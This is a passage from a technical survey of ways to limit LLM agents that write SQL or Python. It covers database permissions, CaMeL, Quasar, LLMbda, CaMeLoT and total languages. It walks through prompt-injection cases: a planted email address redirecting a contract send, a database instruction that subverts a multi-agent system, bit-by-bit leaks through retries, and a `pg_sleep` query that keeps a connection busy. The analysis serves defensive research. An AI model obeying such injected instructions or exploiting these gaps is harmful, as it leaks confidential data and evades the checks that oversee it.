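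Calling a model weakens the restrictions on a query. If another company hosts the model, the query sends contract text to that company, which is an effect. A hidden instruction in a contract could also change the model's answer for that contract's row. It couldn't change the rest of the query, which the agent wrote beforehand, but a free-form answer could carry the instruction back to the agent. The developer can reduce that risk by making the function that calls the model return only a number of days.

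### Limiting effects with database permissions

Databases control effects, such as deleting a table with `DROP TABLE customers`, through the permissions of the account that runs the query. HeimdaLLM's *Safely executing LLM-generated SQL* compares several ways of doing this:

- **Read-only account:** The agent can't change anything, but it can still read everything.
- **Restricted account:** The administrator grants access to particular tables, and in some databases to particular columns. This can hide bank details from the agent, but it can't show each manager only their own customers.
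- **Row-level security:** The database adds a condition to every query, so that an account sees only the rows that meet it. Not all databases support this, and complicated rules are easy to get wrong.
- **Separate copy:** The agent gets its own small database, which contains only what the user may see. The developer has to keep every copy up to date.

Administrators also commonly use views, which are stored queries that behave like tables. For example, an administrator can let the agent query a view of late invoices without giving it access to the full invoice table.

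These methods work best in combination. HeimdaLLM marks down row-level security because it doesn't stop an agent from deleting a table, but a read-only account does. In PostgreSQL, an administrator could set up both for an account manager called Lee:

```sql
GRANT SELECT ON customers, contracts TO lee;
ALTER TABLE contracts ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;
CREATE POLICY own_contracts ON contracts
    FOR SELECT USING (manager = current_user);
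```

An agent that connects as `lee` and asks for every contract receives only the contracts of Lee's customers. This does much to enforce the accounts policy, under which contract text may reach only the manager responsible. The company could run a separate agent for each manager and give each agent a mail function that writes only to that manager. Lee's agent could then neither read other managers' contracts nor mail Lee's to anyone else. This works because the policy allows each contract only one recipient, provided the agents share no memory or files. It would not suit an agent that had to compare contracts across the whole company.

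Telling the model in its prompt to write only `SELECT` statements is much weaker than restricting the database account's permissions, which apply whatever the model writes. The model may make a mistake or follow a hidden instruction in a row it has read. According to HeimdaLLM, attackers can easily get past a second model that checks for such tricks. Even if the model follows the prompt, a `SELECT` statement can do harm by returning every customer's bank details or by calling PostgreSQL's `pg_sleep(999999)`, which keeps a connection busy for over eleven days.

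*LuthorSQL* (2026), a system for answering questions in SQL, limits its agent through both software and instructions. The agent queries the database through a read-only tool that shows at most 20 rows of any result. It is also instructed in its prompt to run no more than eight queries per question and not to use the web. A developer who had to rely on the prompt's rules would want software to enforce them as well.

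Permissions control a query's effects but generally not its computation. An administrator can forbid an account to delete rows but usually can't forbid it to use recursion. To keep an agent to basic SQL, the developer needs a checker that parses each query before it runs, as STELP does for Python. A checker can also reject queries that use forbidden tables or functions, or add a row limit. HeimdaLLM, itself such a checker, considers this and separate copies the two most promising methods. It concedes that SQL is complicated and varies between products, so determined attackers may find queries that the checker misjudges.

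### How SQL compares with Python and the shell

Few experiments compare SQL agents directly with agents that use another language. More experiments compare single programs that a model writes to answer a question.

Hu, Hou and colleagues (*Benchmarking Text-to-Python against Text-to-SQL*, 2026) started from 1,534 questions in BIRD, a standard test of SQL writing. They exported the databases to files and had models answer the same questions in either SQL or Python with pandas, a library for working with tables. Hill, Chorasiya and colleagues (*BIRD-Persona*, 2026) reworded these questions as business users and technical experts would phrase them, and tested nine models. Hasegawa, Sampat and colleagues (*Data Analysis in the Wild*, 2026) wrote their own questions about public government data and compared SQL and Python on the 145 with text answers.

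| Test | Model | Correct with SQL | Correct with Python |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hu and colleagues | Qwen2.5-Coder (7B) | 52.9% | 36.0% |
| Hu and colleagues | Qwen3-Max | 63.1% | 63.4% |
| Hill and colleagues | Gemini 2.5 Flash | 74.1% | 67.4% |
| Hill and colleagues | GPT-5.1 | 72.1% | 63.4% |
| Hasegawa and colleagues | Gemini 2.5 Flash | 24.1% | 54.5% |
| Hasegawa and colleagues | GPT-4o | 14.5% | 30.3% |

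Gemini 2.5 Flash did better with SQL than with Python on one test, but more than twice as well with Python on another, so much of the difference probably comes from the tests. Every BIRD question has an SQL query as its reference answer, so SQL can answer all of them. Hasegawa and colleagues produced their reference answers with Python, and their files were messier, with numbers stored as text and dates in several formats. They also left out questions that asked for a chart, which SQL can't draw. None of these tests measures what share of an office's real questions SQL could answer.

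On the BIRD questions, SQL seems easier for models to get right. Hill and colleagues found it ahead for eight of the nine models, by 3 to 21 percentage points, and it stayed ahead on the most complex questions. But *Pi-SQL* (2025), which has a model draft Python to guide its SQL, found Python ahead on the questions that BIRD rates as challenging. Hu and colleagues traced 17.5 percent of the Python errors to faulty logic, compared with 0.3 percent of the SQL errors. The rates differ because a Python program has to spell out steps that a database handles itself. Misread conditions caused about a third of the errors in each language.

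Hu and colleagues conclude that models do as well in Python as in SQL once they have enough information about what the question means. With clarifications supplied, a mid-sized Qwen3 model scored about 73 percent in both languages. But the result for the largest model, Qwen3-Max, doesn't fit that conclusion, since it scored 80 percent with SQL and only 73 percent with Python. The clarifications may also have favoured SQL, because they came from a model that had access to the correct SQL. The instructions for Python barred the models from defining functions, which removes one of Python's usual advantages. The reference answers in such tests are also unreliable, since Hu and colleagues had to correct 259 of BIRD's.

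The clearest comparison of agents is *Testing if "bash is all you need"* (Goyal, 2026), from Braintrust, a company that sells software for testing AI systems. Goyal gave three agents the same questions about a collection of software bug reports and proposed code changes. One queried a database in SQL, another used the Bash command shell on 68,000 files, and the third had only tools for searching and reading files. The SQL agent answered every question correctly at an average cost of $0.51, in 45 seconds. The shell agent got 52.7 percent right, at $3.34 and 401 seconds, and the agent with only file tools got 63 percent right.

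These first figures exaggerate SQL's advantage. Some shell commands had timed out because of a fault in the shell software, and five of the reference answers were wrong or ambiguous. Correcting these problems narrowed the gap considerably. An agent with both SQL and the shell was then the most reliable, since it checked its query results by searching the files, though it used about twice as many tokens as the SQL agent. Arize, which also sells software for monitoring AI systems, reports a similar result from comparing an agent that queried a database in SQL with one that was given the same database as simulated files. The SQL agent was more accurate overall, but the two were close on simple lookups.

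In all of these tests, the agent reads data and answers questions. Ma and colleagues found that companies' data agents often depend on outside services such as email, but they left out tasks that need those services because live services make results hard to reproduce. They also included no tasks that change a database. The evidence therefore supports using SQL for the accounts agent's first few steps, but it doesn't show how well an SQL agent would complete the whole job.

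Some designs use SQL to fetch data and Python to work with it. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a typical SQL agent that also has a Python interpreter, which it uses to analyse query results, check its answers and draw charts. In *ProSPy* (2026), SQL fetches and lightly summarises the data, and Python does the more complex analysis on the saved files. A read-only account still protects the database in these designs, but it doesn't control what happens to rows once they reach Python.

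## Can an interpreter enforce the limits while the program runs?

An interpreter carries out every step of a program, so it can keep track of a piece of text after the program has read it, which neither a sandbox nor a database account does. It can record where each value came from and check that record before anything leaves the program. It can also hold back effects until a person approves them, while letting calculation continue.

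### A planner that never reads the data

Prompt injection works when the model that reads untrusted text also decides what to do next. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed dividing these jobs between two models. A planning model sees the user's request and chooses the tool calls, but never reads untrusted data. A quarantined model reads that data, but has no tools and only returns an answer. An instruction hidden in the data can corrupt that answer, but it can't make the quarantined model send an email.

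CaMeL, a 2025 system from Google DeepMind, combines this pattern with code actions. The planning model writes the entire program before any tool runs, and the program calls the quarantined model as if it were a function. CaMeL's own interpreter then runs the program. It accepts only a subset of Python that excludes user-defined functions and open-ended `while` loops. The accounts agent would therefore have to trace owners with a `for` loop over a list.

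*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls the resulting property control-flow integrity. The data a tool returns may determine which branch of the program runs, but it can't add a branch that the planning model didn't write.

How much protection this gives depends on what the branches allow. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) tested CaMeL on a request to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With CaMeL's policy checks turned off, the planning model sometimes wrote a program with a branch for every tool. Whoever wrote the file could then choose among the tools, and an attack succeeded this way in two runs.

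Planning in advance also makes the program harder to write. An ordinary agent can read a tool's output before deciding how to handle it, but CaMeL's planning model has to write the handling code without seeing any output. Peters-Gill and colleagues therefore had to add a description of the return format to every tool, as CaMeL's designers had done. If a contract were oddly worded, the accounts agent's planning model couldn't print the text to see what went wrong, and would have to rely on the quarantined model to find the notice period.

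### From an email to a refused call

Separating the models protects the plan but not the data that passes through it. An attacker can leave the plan alone and change a value that the plan gives to a tool, as Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues explain in *CaMeLoT* (2026). CaMeL's interpreter therefore labels every value with its sources and who may read it. CaMeL's designers call these labels capabilities, but unlike capabilities in Miller's sense, the labels don't grant any power to act.

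For example, a user might ask the accounts agent to send the contract of a customer called Acme to the account manager named in Acme's latest email. The planning model could write:

```python
message = get_latest_email("Acme")
address = ask_quarantined_model(
    f"Find the account manager's address: {message}",
    EmailAddress)
contract = read_contract("Acme")
send_email(address, contract)
```

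The manager is Lee, but a hidden line in the email gives `audit@supplier.example` as the manager's address. The false address would travel through the program like this:

1. `get_latest_email` returns the message, and the interpreter labels it as coming from an outside sender.
2. The quarantined model believes the hidden line and returns the false address. The `EmailAddress` type forces it to return an address and not, say, a paragraph of instructions. The address inherits the message's label because the model derived it from the message.
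3. `read_contract` returns the contract, with a label that names Lee as its only permitted reader.
4. The program calls `send_email`. Before the tool runs, the interpreter passes the tool's name, its inputs and their labels to the policy, which is a Python function that a developer wrote. The policy finds that the address doesn't belong to a permitted reader of the contract, and refuses the call.

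The attacker put a false address into the program, but the contract was not sent. This protection does not depend on detecting whether the email looks suspicious. Reversing the contract text or splitting it over several messages would not help the attacker either, because each new string would inherit the contract's label.

A developer could write a stricter policy that accepts a recipient's address only from a trusted source. It would stop this attack too, but it would refuse the call even if Acme's email correctly named Lee. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes altered recipients and file names as typical of what CaMeL's labels are meant to catch, but legitimate documents often supply recipients and file names too.

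Checking each call as it happens lets the policy use facts that weren't known when the planning model wrote the program, such as the address in the email. But the program may have done part of its work before the interpreter refuses a call. Nikolaou and colleagues also check the whole plan before it starts, for rules that don't depend on such facts.

### Where CaMeL's tracking stops

CaMeL's interpreter can track values only inside its own program. Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated the problem with three CaMeL agents. One could give tasks to the other two, one of which had access to a database of job applicants while the other sent messages. The user asked the system to send Julie a summary of the applicants on Slack, but someone had planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outsider as well.

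The attack succeeded even though CaMeL was protecting each agent separately. The coordinating agent and the database agent both followed their original plans, but the coordinating agent put the summary, which contained the hidden instruction, into its request to the messaging agent. The messaging agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so its planning model read the instruction and wrote a program that sent an extra email.

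Peters-Gill and colleagues ran this test without any policies on data, so the failure it shows is in the two-model split, not the labels. Their solution gives each agent separate channels for instructions and data. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, and labels stay attached to data as it passes from one agent to the next.

A single agent's tracking can have gaps too. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) argues that Python is a poor basis for strong guarantees because its types can change during a run, errors can redirect the program, and programs can inspect and alter themselves. It recommends a purpose-built language with bounded loops and simple conditions. Garby and colleagues found an error in CaMeL's interpreter, which treated untrusted text as trusted once a program had inserted it into a larger string. Such errors are hard to find because CaMeL's rules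 for labels are defined only in the interpreter's code.

### Quasar: separating calculation from calls

*A Fast, Reliable, and Secure Programming Language for LLM Agents* (Mell, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) introduces Quasar, a language for code actions built around the distinction between pure functions and effects. Code inside a Quasar program can only calculate. Anything else, including printing, requires an external call to a Python function.

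The interpreter runs the internal code by repeatedly replacing part of it with something simpler that means the same, until only the result is left. The order of these replacements doesn't affect the result, so the interpreter can work on whichever part is ready.

Mell and colleagues illustrate this with the question "Is there an alcoholic drink in this image?" A model might answer it with this program:

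```python
drinks = image.find("drink")
found = False
for drink in drinks:
    if drink.simple_query("Does this have alcohol?") == "yes":
        found = True
return found
```

Here `find` calls an object detector, and `simple_query` puts a question about part of the picture to another model. For an image with two drinks, Quasar proceeds as follows:

1. The interpreter calls `find`, which returns two pieces of the image.
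2. It replaces the loop with two copies of the `if` statement, one for each piece.
3. Both `simple_query` calls now have everything they need, so the interpreter starts them at the same time. Python would wait for the first answer before making the second call.
4. The answers are "no" and "yes". The interpreter puts them in place of the calls, works out that only the second comparison is true, and reduces the program to `return True`.

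The same method reduces interruptions when a user has to approve external calls. Quasar does all the calculation it can, collects every call that is ready, and presents them to the user together. In this example, the user would get two requests, compared with three if each call were approved separately. With ten drinks in the picture, the user would still get two requests instead of eleven. If the user rejects a batch, the program ends.

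### Translating Python into Quasar

Quasar code consists of nested lists of numbers and operation names, and models write it badly. In the 2025 tests, only 28 percent of the programs a model wrote directly in Quasar ran without an error. Mell and colleagues therefore ask the model for Python and translate it with a compiler. The model has to avoid some Python features, such as classes, but most code actions don't need them.

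Variables are harder to translate. A Python program can change the value of `found`, but a Quasar variable keeps the value it first receives. The compiler solves this by giving each version of the variable its own name. In Python-like notation, the `if` statement becomes:

```python
found0 = False
found1 = True if answer == "yes" else found0
```

The conditional now produces a value whichever branch runs, and the program never changes anything. For a loop, the compiler passes the latest version of `found` from one item to the next.

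In the 2025 tests, 91 percent of translated programs ran successfully, compared with 99.7 percent of ordinary Python programs. Counting failed programs as wrong answers, the translated programs answered about 64 percent of the image questions correctly and the Python programs about 70 percent. Among programs that ran, both groups answered 70.6 percent correctly. *QUASAR*, a 2026 revision, reports a much smaller gap. With GPT-5, 97.9 percent of the translated programs ran, and they answered 71.4 percent of all the questions correctly, compared with 71.8 percent for Python.

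### How much time and attention Quasar saves

Mell and colleagues tested Quasar on 1,000 questions from GQA, a dataset about everyday photographs. For the revised version, they also used AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking, chat and travel tasks. The best-known figures for Quasar, a 42 percent cut in execution time and a 52 percent cut in approval requests, cover only the GQA programs that could benefit. Many programs make only one call, or need the answer to each call before making the next, so Quasar can't combine their calls.

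| Version and test | Measure | Programs that could improve | Average cut for those programs | Average cut for all programs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2025, GQA | Execution time | 41% | 42% | 16% |
| 2025, GQA | Approval requests | 42% | 52% | 22% |
| 2026, GQA | Execution time | 49% | 37% | 18% |
| 2026, GQA | Approval requests | 50% | 53% | 26% |
| 2026, AgentDojo | Execution time | 38% | 54% | 27% |
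| 2026, AgentDojo | Approval requests | 57% | 44% | 26% |

Quasar reduces approval requests and execution time much more when a program makes many independent calls. On 80 research questions from the BrowseComp-Plus benchmark, each with about 100 documents to search, it cut approval requests by 97 percent and execution time by 93 percent.

Mell and colleagues argue that fewer approval requests improve security because people who face constant requests stop reading them. That seems plausible, but they counted requests and didn't test whether users made better decisions. A user who gets 97 percent fewer requests still has to judge the same calls, which now arrive in long lists. Mell and colleagues also concede that users may not understand the calls they are asked to approve.

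The accounts agent could use Quasar to trace every owner, read all the contracts and then ask the user to approve fifty emails at once. The user could see each address and message, but Quasar doesn't record where either came from. If one of the addresses came from a supplier's email, the user couldn't tell from the request. Quasar limits when effects happen and who approves them, but has no protection of its own against prompt injection.

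Running calls out of order also creates a new kind of mistake. Suppose a program corrects a manager's address in the customer database, then calls a function that looks up the address and sends an email. If the second call doesn't use the result of the first, Quasar may start both together, and the email could go to the old address. The developer has to make the dependency explicit, for example by passing the update's result to the email function.

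### What a branch that does not run can reveal

The image program can illustrate an older problem with labels. Suppose the answers about alcohol are secret, and an interpreter labels values as the Python version runs. The program first sets `found` to `False`, which is public. If one of the drinks is alcoholic, the program then sets `found` to `True` inside a branch that depends on a secret, so the interpreter labels the new value secret.

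But if none of the drinks is alcoholic, that branch never runs, so `found` stays `False` and keeps its public label. A person who may read only public values can then tell that the image has no alcoholic drinks. The interpreter can't prevent this leak by labeling the assignment, because it never carries the assignment out. Garby and colleagues trace the problem to work by Fenton in 1974 and Denning in 1976.

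CaMeL handles the simpler case, where a program sends an email inside a branch that depends on a secret. The interpreter takes the condition into account when it checks the call, and the policy can refuse it. But when a branch changes a variable, CaMeL updates the variable's label only if that branch runs. If the branch doesn't run, the variable's unchanged value can reveal the secret without being labeled as secret. Programs often set a variable to `False` and change it later, so a planning model could cause this leak by accident.

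One yes-or-no answer may not matter much, but CaMeL lets the planning model try again after a failure. An ordinary Python loop outside the interpreter controls these attempts. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, and the loop carries that information into the next attempt without a label. Over many attempts, a program could reveal a whole secret one bit at a time. CaMeL censors error messages to reduce this risk, but without a formal guarantee. Deliberately exploiting the leak would require a program written for that purpose. Because CaMeL's planning model doesn't read untrusted data, such a program is more likely to come from a faulty or compromised model than from instructions hidden in an email.

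A type checker can avoid the problem by examining both branches before the program runs. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) gives the example of Jif, a language that rejects insecure flows this way. Run-time systems can instead stop a program that tries to change a public variable in a secret branch, but this also stops some harmless programs. A method called permissive upgrade stops fewer of them by tracking values that are only partly public.

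### LLMbda: labels on every value

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda so that they could prove its labels reliable. The language extends the lambda calculus with commands for talking to a language model. A program can send a prompt, run the reply as code, continue in a temporary copy of the conversation, or clear the conversation. LLMbda has no type checker and allows unlimited recursion, so it is Turing-complete.

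CaMeL's two-model split is part of its architecture, but an LLMbda program can create the split itself. A short function called `quarantine` copies the conversation, clears the copy, uses it to ask the model about some untrusted text, and returns the answer, so the main conversation never contains the text.

In the simplest version, a label marks a value as untrusted, secret, both or neither. A result inherits the marks of everything that went into it. The conversation also has a label, which covers every message the program has sent. If a model reads an untrusted email and then writes code, everything that code computes is untrusted too.

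LLMbda avoids most leaks from unused branches because its variables never change. An `if` returns a value, and that value inherits the label of the condition whichever branch produced it. In the image example, `found` would be secret whether it was `True` or `False`. Quasar's compiler rewrites `if` into much the same form, but does so to let calls run in parallel.

The conversation is the exception, since a program can add to it or clear it. LLMbda therefore forbids a program to change a public conversation from inside a secret branch. Garby and colleagues show a program that tells a model to remember that *x* is false and then, only if a secret is true, tells it that *x* is true. The interpreter stops the program at the second message. Anyone who sees the program stop still learns the secret, but the program can't catch the error and use it to extract another bit.

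### What the noninterference theorem guarantees

The central result about LLMbda is a noninterference theorem. It concerns an observer who may see values with some labels but not others. If a program runs twice on inputs that differ only in data the observer may not see, and both runs always finish, the observer will see the same results with the same probabilities. The theorem involves probabilities because a language model can answer the same prompt in different ways.

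The theorem is termination-insensitive, so it doesn't cover what an observer could learn from whether a program finishes. A secret may determine whether a program runs forever or stops because of a policy violation, as in the example with *x*. The theorem also covers only results, so an observer could still learn something from how long a program takes.

To state this exactly, let *μ*(*q*) and *ν*(*q*) be the probabilities that the two runs finish with the visible result *q*. Each set of probabilities may add up to less than 1, and the rest is the chance of not finishing. The theorem says that there is a third set of probabilities, *ω*, such that for every *q*

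*μ*(*q*) ≤ *ω*(*q*) and *ν*(*q*) ≤ *ω*(*q*),

while *ω* adds up to no more than 1. If both runs always finish, *μ* and *ν* must each equal *ω*, so they are identical. Otherwise the distance between them, measured as half the sum of the differences |*μ*(*q*) − *ν*(*q*)|, is at most the average chance of not finishing. If one run fails to finish 10 percent of the time and the other 20 percent, the distance is at most 0.15. A program that almost always finishes can therefore leak very little in a single run.

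The theorem applies to every LLMbda program, including code that a model writes during the run. Garby and colleagues wrote the interpreter in Lean, a language for computer-checked proofs. They also proved the theorem in Lean, whereas the CaMeL paper left a formal treatment to future work.

In one of their examples, Alice asked an agent to remind Bob of a meeting, but someone had added a request for a cancellation to an email from Bob. An ordinary agent that read the email sent the cancellation. In the protected version, the model wrote its program before reading the email, and the email tool required the subject and text to be trusted. That agent sent the correct reminder. By the theorem, no change to Bob's email could have altered a subject or text that passed the check. An attacker could still have redirected the reminder, however, because the program took the recipient's address from the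 email, which the policy allowed.

### Making strict labels usable

Strict labels can quickly make an agent useless. If a program fails while handling untrusted data, the error message is untrusted, and so is any new program that the model writes after reading it. The new program then can't use a tool that accepts only trusted inputs.

Randori, an agent that Garby and colleagues wrote in LLMbda, gets around this by having the model test its program on simulated data first. During these tests, reading a file returns placeholder text and sending money does nothing. The model can correct its program as often as the developer allows, then writes a final version for the real data. If that version fails, the model cannot repair it.

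Some tasks also require an agent to act on untrusted information, such as an invoice from a supplier. LLMbda has an `endorse` command that relabels untrusted data as trusted. A careful program might use it when a quarantined model has sorted an email into one of eight categories. An attacker could influence the choice of category, but could convey at most three bits of information that way. A second theorem shows that endorsing data this way can't weaken the protection of secrets.

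However, nothing forces the planning model to be careful. In AgentDojo's banking tests, Randori resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. In both failures, the program had endorsed payment instructions from a file that an attacker had replaced. The user had asked the agent to make whatever payment the file specified, so labels alone could have prevented the payment only by blocking the task.

The theorems also assume that developers have labelled the data correctly and put checks in the tools. If a company using LLMbda forgot to label its contracts folder, the agent could email any contract to a stranger and the theorems would still hold. Garby and colleagues ran their tests with tools that were LLMbda functions acting on a simulated bank account, and they acknowledge that they haven't yet modelled external tools and data.

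## What is gained by ruling out unbounded loops and recursion?

An interpreter that checks calls one at a time may stop a program halfway through. A developer who wants to know beforehand what a program will do has to analyse its text, and unbounded loops and recursion make that harder. CaMeL's subset of Python has no open-ended `while` loops, and basic SQL has no loops at all. Ruling out unbounded loops and recursion can guarantee that a program finishes and make some checks simpler, but it does little to control the program's effects.

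### What no checker can decide

The halting problem asks whether a given program will finish on a given input. No algorithm can answer correctly for every program in a Turing-complete language. To see why, suppose someone had written a function `halts(p, x)` that was always right. A programmer could then write this:

```python
def contrary(p):
    if halts(p, p):
        while True:
            pass
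```

When `contrary` runs on its own text, it loops forever if `halts` predicts that it will finish, and finishes at once if `halts` predicts that it will run forever. Either prediction is wrong, so `halts` can't exist.

Rice (1953), in *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems*, proved a much broader result about properties that depend only on the function a program computes, meaning that programs with identical behaviour on every input either all have the property or all lack it. If some programs have such a property and others don't, no algorithm can decide for every program whether it has the property. One example is "returns zero for every input". The result doesn't apply to "contains the word `while`", because that depends on the program's text, which a checker can search.

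Sending an email is an effect, not part of the function a program computes, but a similar argument applies. A program could simulate another program, without carrying out its effects, and then email a contract to a stranger. It would send the email only if the simulated program finished. A checker that could always predict whether the email would be sent would therefore solve the halting problem.

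These results rule out only a checker that always gives an answer and is never wrong. A checker can still reject every unsafe program if it also rejects some safe ones. The Haskell calculator that Zhou and colleagues describe works this way. It would reject a program that loops forever and then deletes a file, even though the deletion could never happen. So developers don't have to give up general computation to get reliable checks. The practical question is how many useful programs a checker rejects.

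### What a total language guarantees

A total language avoids the halting problem by admitting only programs that finish. Turner's *Total Functional Programming* (2004) proposed a simple discipline for designing one. In such languages, a function typically may call itself only on a smaller part of its input, such as the rest of a list after the first item, so the calls stop when a finite list runs out. Turner keeps finite data separate from codata, which may be infinite, such as a stream of incoming emails. A program can keep handling the stream for as long as someone asks for the next item, but it must produce each item in finite time.

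Turner wanted programs to obey the ordinary rules of algebra. Most functional languages let a programmer define `loop(n) = 1 + loop(n)`, which never finishes. Subtracting `loop(n)` from both sides gives 0 = 1. A total language rejects the definition, so the rules hold. A compiler can then delete any pure calculation whose result the program doesn't use. In a general language, that deletion might turn a program that never finishes into one that does.

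Guaranteed finishing can also help with security. A total version of LLMbda, for example, could no longer leak a secret through an endless loop.

Many tasks that seem to need an unbounded loop have a natural limit. The accounts agent doesn't know how many holding companies stand above a customer, but there can't be more of them than there are companies in the table. It could therefore find the owner like this:

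```python
owner = c.id
for _ in parent:
    if parent[owner] is not None:
        owner = parent[owner]
```

The loop runs once per company, which is always enough, and it stops even if two companies are recorded as each other's parent. But it wastes a lot of work. With 10,000 companies and 10,000 overdue customers, it makes 100 million passes, even if no chain has more than four links.

A language that is not Turing-complete is not necessarily total. Increment's *It doesn’t have to be Turing complete to be useful* (2018), an article by the software engineer Adam Vartanian, gives the example of a language whose only instruction is to loop forever.

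Totality also doesn't settle other questions about a program. For example, a program can take a number *n*, simulate another program for *n* steps, and return 1 if that program has finished by then and 0 if it hasn't. This always finishes, and even quite simple total languages can express it, but deciding whether it returns 1 for some *n* is the halting problem. To answer questions like this exactly, a checker needs a simpler kind of program, such as one with a finite number of possible states.

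### safescript's fixed graphs

The small agent language safescript restricts programs more than most total languages do. Every program is a fixed graph of operations, with arrows showing which results feed into which. There are no loops, and the parser rejects any function that calls itself, directly or through others. A program can repeat an operation only with `map`, `filter` and `reduce`, which work through a finite list. The language's author acknowledges that it can't express some computations, such as sorting a list.

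The names of every secret a program reads and every server it contacts must also appear in the program's text, not be calculated while it runs. Before the program starts, the software can therefore produce a signature that lists the secrets, the servers and the flows of data between them. If an updated program sent a password to a new server, the signature would change and the build would fail.

The author calls the language provably safe and argues that it needs no sandbox. The signature looks useful, but its usefulness comes as much from the fixed names and the short list of operations as from the lack of loops. If the language allowed loops but gave programs no way to calculate a server's name, software could still list every server a program might contact. The guarantee also depends on the parser and interpreter having no serious bugs.

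A signature would not enforce the accounts policy either, because it would show contract text flowing to the company's mail server but not the message's recipient.

### How CaMeLoT searches every path

CaMeLoT, the system by Nikolaou and colleagues that checks CaMeL's plans before they run, can enforce rules about the order of events. One of their examples is an agent that handles security alerts. It may isolate a computer, meaning cut it off from the network, but only after asking the incident response team for approval. Using the tools from that example, a planning model might write this faulty plan:

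```python
alert = get_last_alert(severity="HIGH")
host = confirm_host(hostname="workstation-17")
ticket = create_incident_ticket(title="Possible compromise")
if alert.host_is_important:
    request_ir_approval(incident=ticket)
isolate_host(hostname=host)
resolve_incident(incident=ticket)
```

CaMeLoT would check it as follows:

1. It parses the plan and turns it into a finite-state machine, a diagram of the points the program can reach and the possible moves between them. Each state records which tool the program is calling, which tools it has already called, and which inputs come from untrusted sources.
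2. At the `if`, the machine can take either branch. CaMeLoT ignores the condition itself. At a loop, the machine can go round again or leave, so a loop over ten items and a loop over a million produce the same few states.
3. A developer has written the policy in temporal logic, which describes how events may follow one another. For isolation, the rule is `AG(call_isolate_host -> request_ir_approval_called)`. `AG` means "in every state on every path", so wherever the plan isolates a computer, it must already have requested approval.
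4. A program called a model checker searches all the states for one that breaks the rule. It finds the path that skips the `if` block and reaches `isolate_host` without a request.
5. CaMeLoT describes this path, called a counterexample, to the planning model and asks it to repair the plan. The model could move the request out of the `if` block. CaMeLoT then checks the new plan, and repeats the process until a plan passes or it runs out of attempts.

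All this happens before any tool runs, so nobody has to reconnect a computer that the agent should not have disconnected. However, CaMeLoT rejects some plans unnecessarily. If every computer in the company counted as important, the faulty plan would always request approval, but CaMeLoT, which doesn't model the condition, would still reject it.

Another limitation is that the rule requires the plan to request approval but not to receive it. CaMeLoT treats each tool as a black box, so a plan that ignored a refusal from `request_ir_approval` would still pass. To enforce a refusal, the tool itself would have to stop the program.

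CaMeLoT doesn't need the ban on unbounded loops to check that approval comes before isolation. It already ignores how many times a loop runs, so it could treat a `while` loop the same way. The ban is more useful for checking that something eventually happens, for instance that the agent resolves or escalates every ticket it opens. In the machine, one path goes round a loop forever and never reaches the steps after it. A checker can safely disregard that path if the language guarantees that loops end, but without that guarantee the program might actually follow it.

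### How well CaMeLoT worked

Nikolaou and colleagues first tried to reproduce CaMeL's own policies for AgentDojo, and could check 22 of the 28 before a plan ran. Most of the rest depend on facts that aren't available until the plan runs, such as who can read a file. They then ran both systems on AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks without attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5 to write the plans.

| Result | Tasks |
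|---|---|
| Both allowed a plan that worked | 42 |
| Both allowed a plan that did not do the task | 22 |
| Both blocked the plan | 17 |
| Only CaMeLoT allowed the plan | 9 |
| Only CaMeL allowed the plan | 7 |

The two systems usually agreed, which suggests that many of CaMeL's checks don't need to wait until the program runs. But the test included no attacks, so every block interrupted a legitimate task. CaMeLoT blocked 24 of the 97 tasks and CaMeL blocked 26. Policy repairs might have allowed some of the tasks CaMeLoT blocked, but Nikolaou and colleagues switched repairs off for this test and don't report how often repairs succeed.

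For the security alerts, the researchers wrote seven rules and altered a safe plan by hand to break each one. CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe plans, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught only the one that passed an untrusted address to a tool. This was expected because they chose rules that CaMeL's checks on individual calls don't naturally express. In another test, Claude Haiku 4.5 wrote unsafe plans in response to four misleading requests, one of which told it to skip approval because time was short. CaMeLoT caught all four plans and CaMeL caught none. A run-time monitor that remembered earlier calls could also have enforced the approval rule, but only by stopping the plan when it reached the isolation step.

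CaMeLoT can also turn a user's request into rules for that task. For example, when a user asks the agent to check recent transactions and change a password if any look suspicious, one rule is that changing the password must remain possible after the check. A language model picks from a fixed set of rule forms, and ordinary software translates its choice into temporal logic. The model identified exactly the right actions for 85 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks. Its mistakes on the other 12 could block a good plan or let a bad one through.

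### Finishing is not enough

A program that always finishes can still take far too long. Three nested passes over a list of 10,000 items take 10<sup>12</sup> steps, which at ten million steps a second is more than a day. A fourth would take over 30 years. Safescript's author argues that its programs need no time limit, but a function passed to `reduce` can itself use `reduce`, so the language's stated rules don't prevent this kind of nesting. Vartanian writes in Increment that "finite isn't a very restrictive limit". He recommends languages built from operations that each make a known number of passes over the data, which give useful bounds on running time.

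A time limit can stop any program in any language. The host starts the program, waits perhaps ten seconds, and ends it if it is still running. The host doesn't have to solve the halting problem, because it never needs to know whether the program would have finished. The drawback is that a time limit can interrupt a correct program after it has sent half of its emails. A total language has the same drawback if its programs can run for days, because the developer will need a time limit there too.

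An agent can run forever even if each of its programs finishes, because the model can always write another one. Limiting the number of rounds prevents this. *λ_A* (Liu, 2026) gives a computer-checked proof that an agent limited to *n* rounds stops within *n* rounds, provided every model or tool call finishes. The limit also caps the cost, so at one cent per model call, an agent limited to 20 rounds can spend at most 20 cents. Liu's calculation assumes one paid call per round, so the cap would be higher for an agent whose tools also charge money.

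A program that is guaranteed to finish can still do harm. Nikolaou and colleagues give an example of an unsafe plan with three statements and no loop. It sends a message to an address that anyone posting in a chat channel could have supplied.

### Why some programs become much longer

A total language can also make programs harder to write. *Old Neglected Theorems Are Still Theorems* (2014), a blog post by the computer scientist Robert Harper, illustrates this with the greatest common divisor of two numbers. For positive numbers, a general-purpose program can keep subtracting the smaller from the larger until they are equal:

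```python
while m != n:
    if m > n:
        m = m - n
    else:
        n = n - m
```

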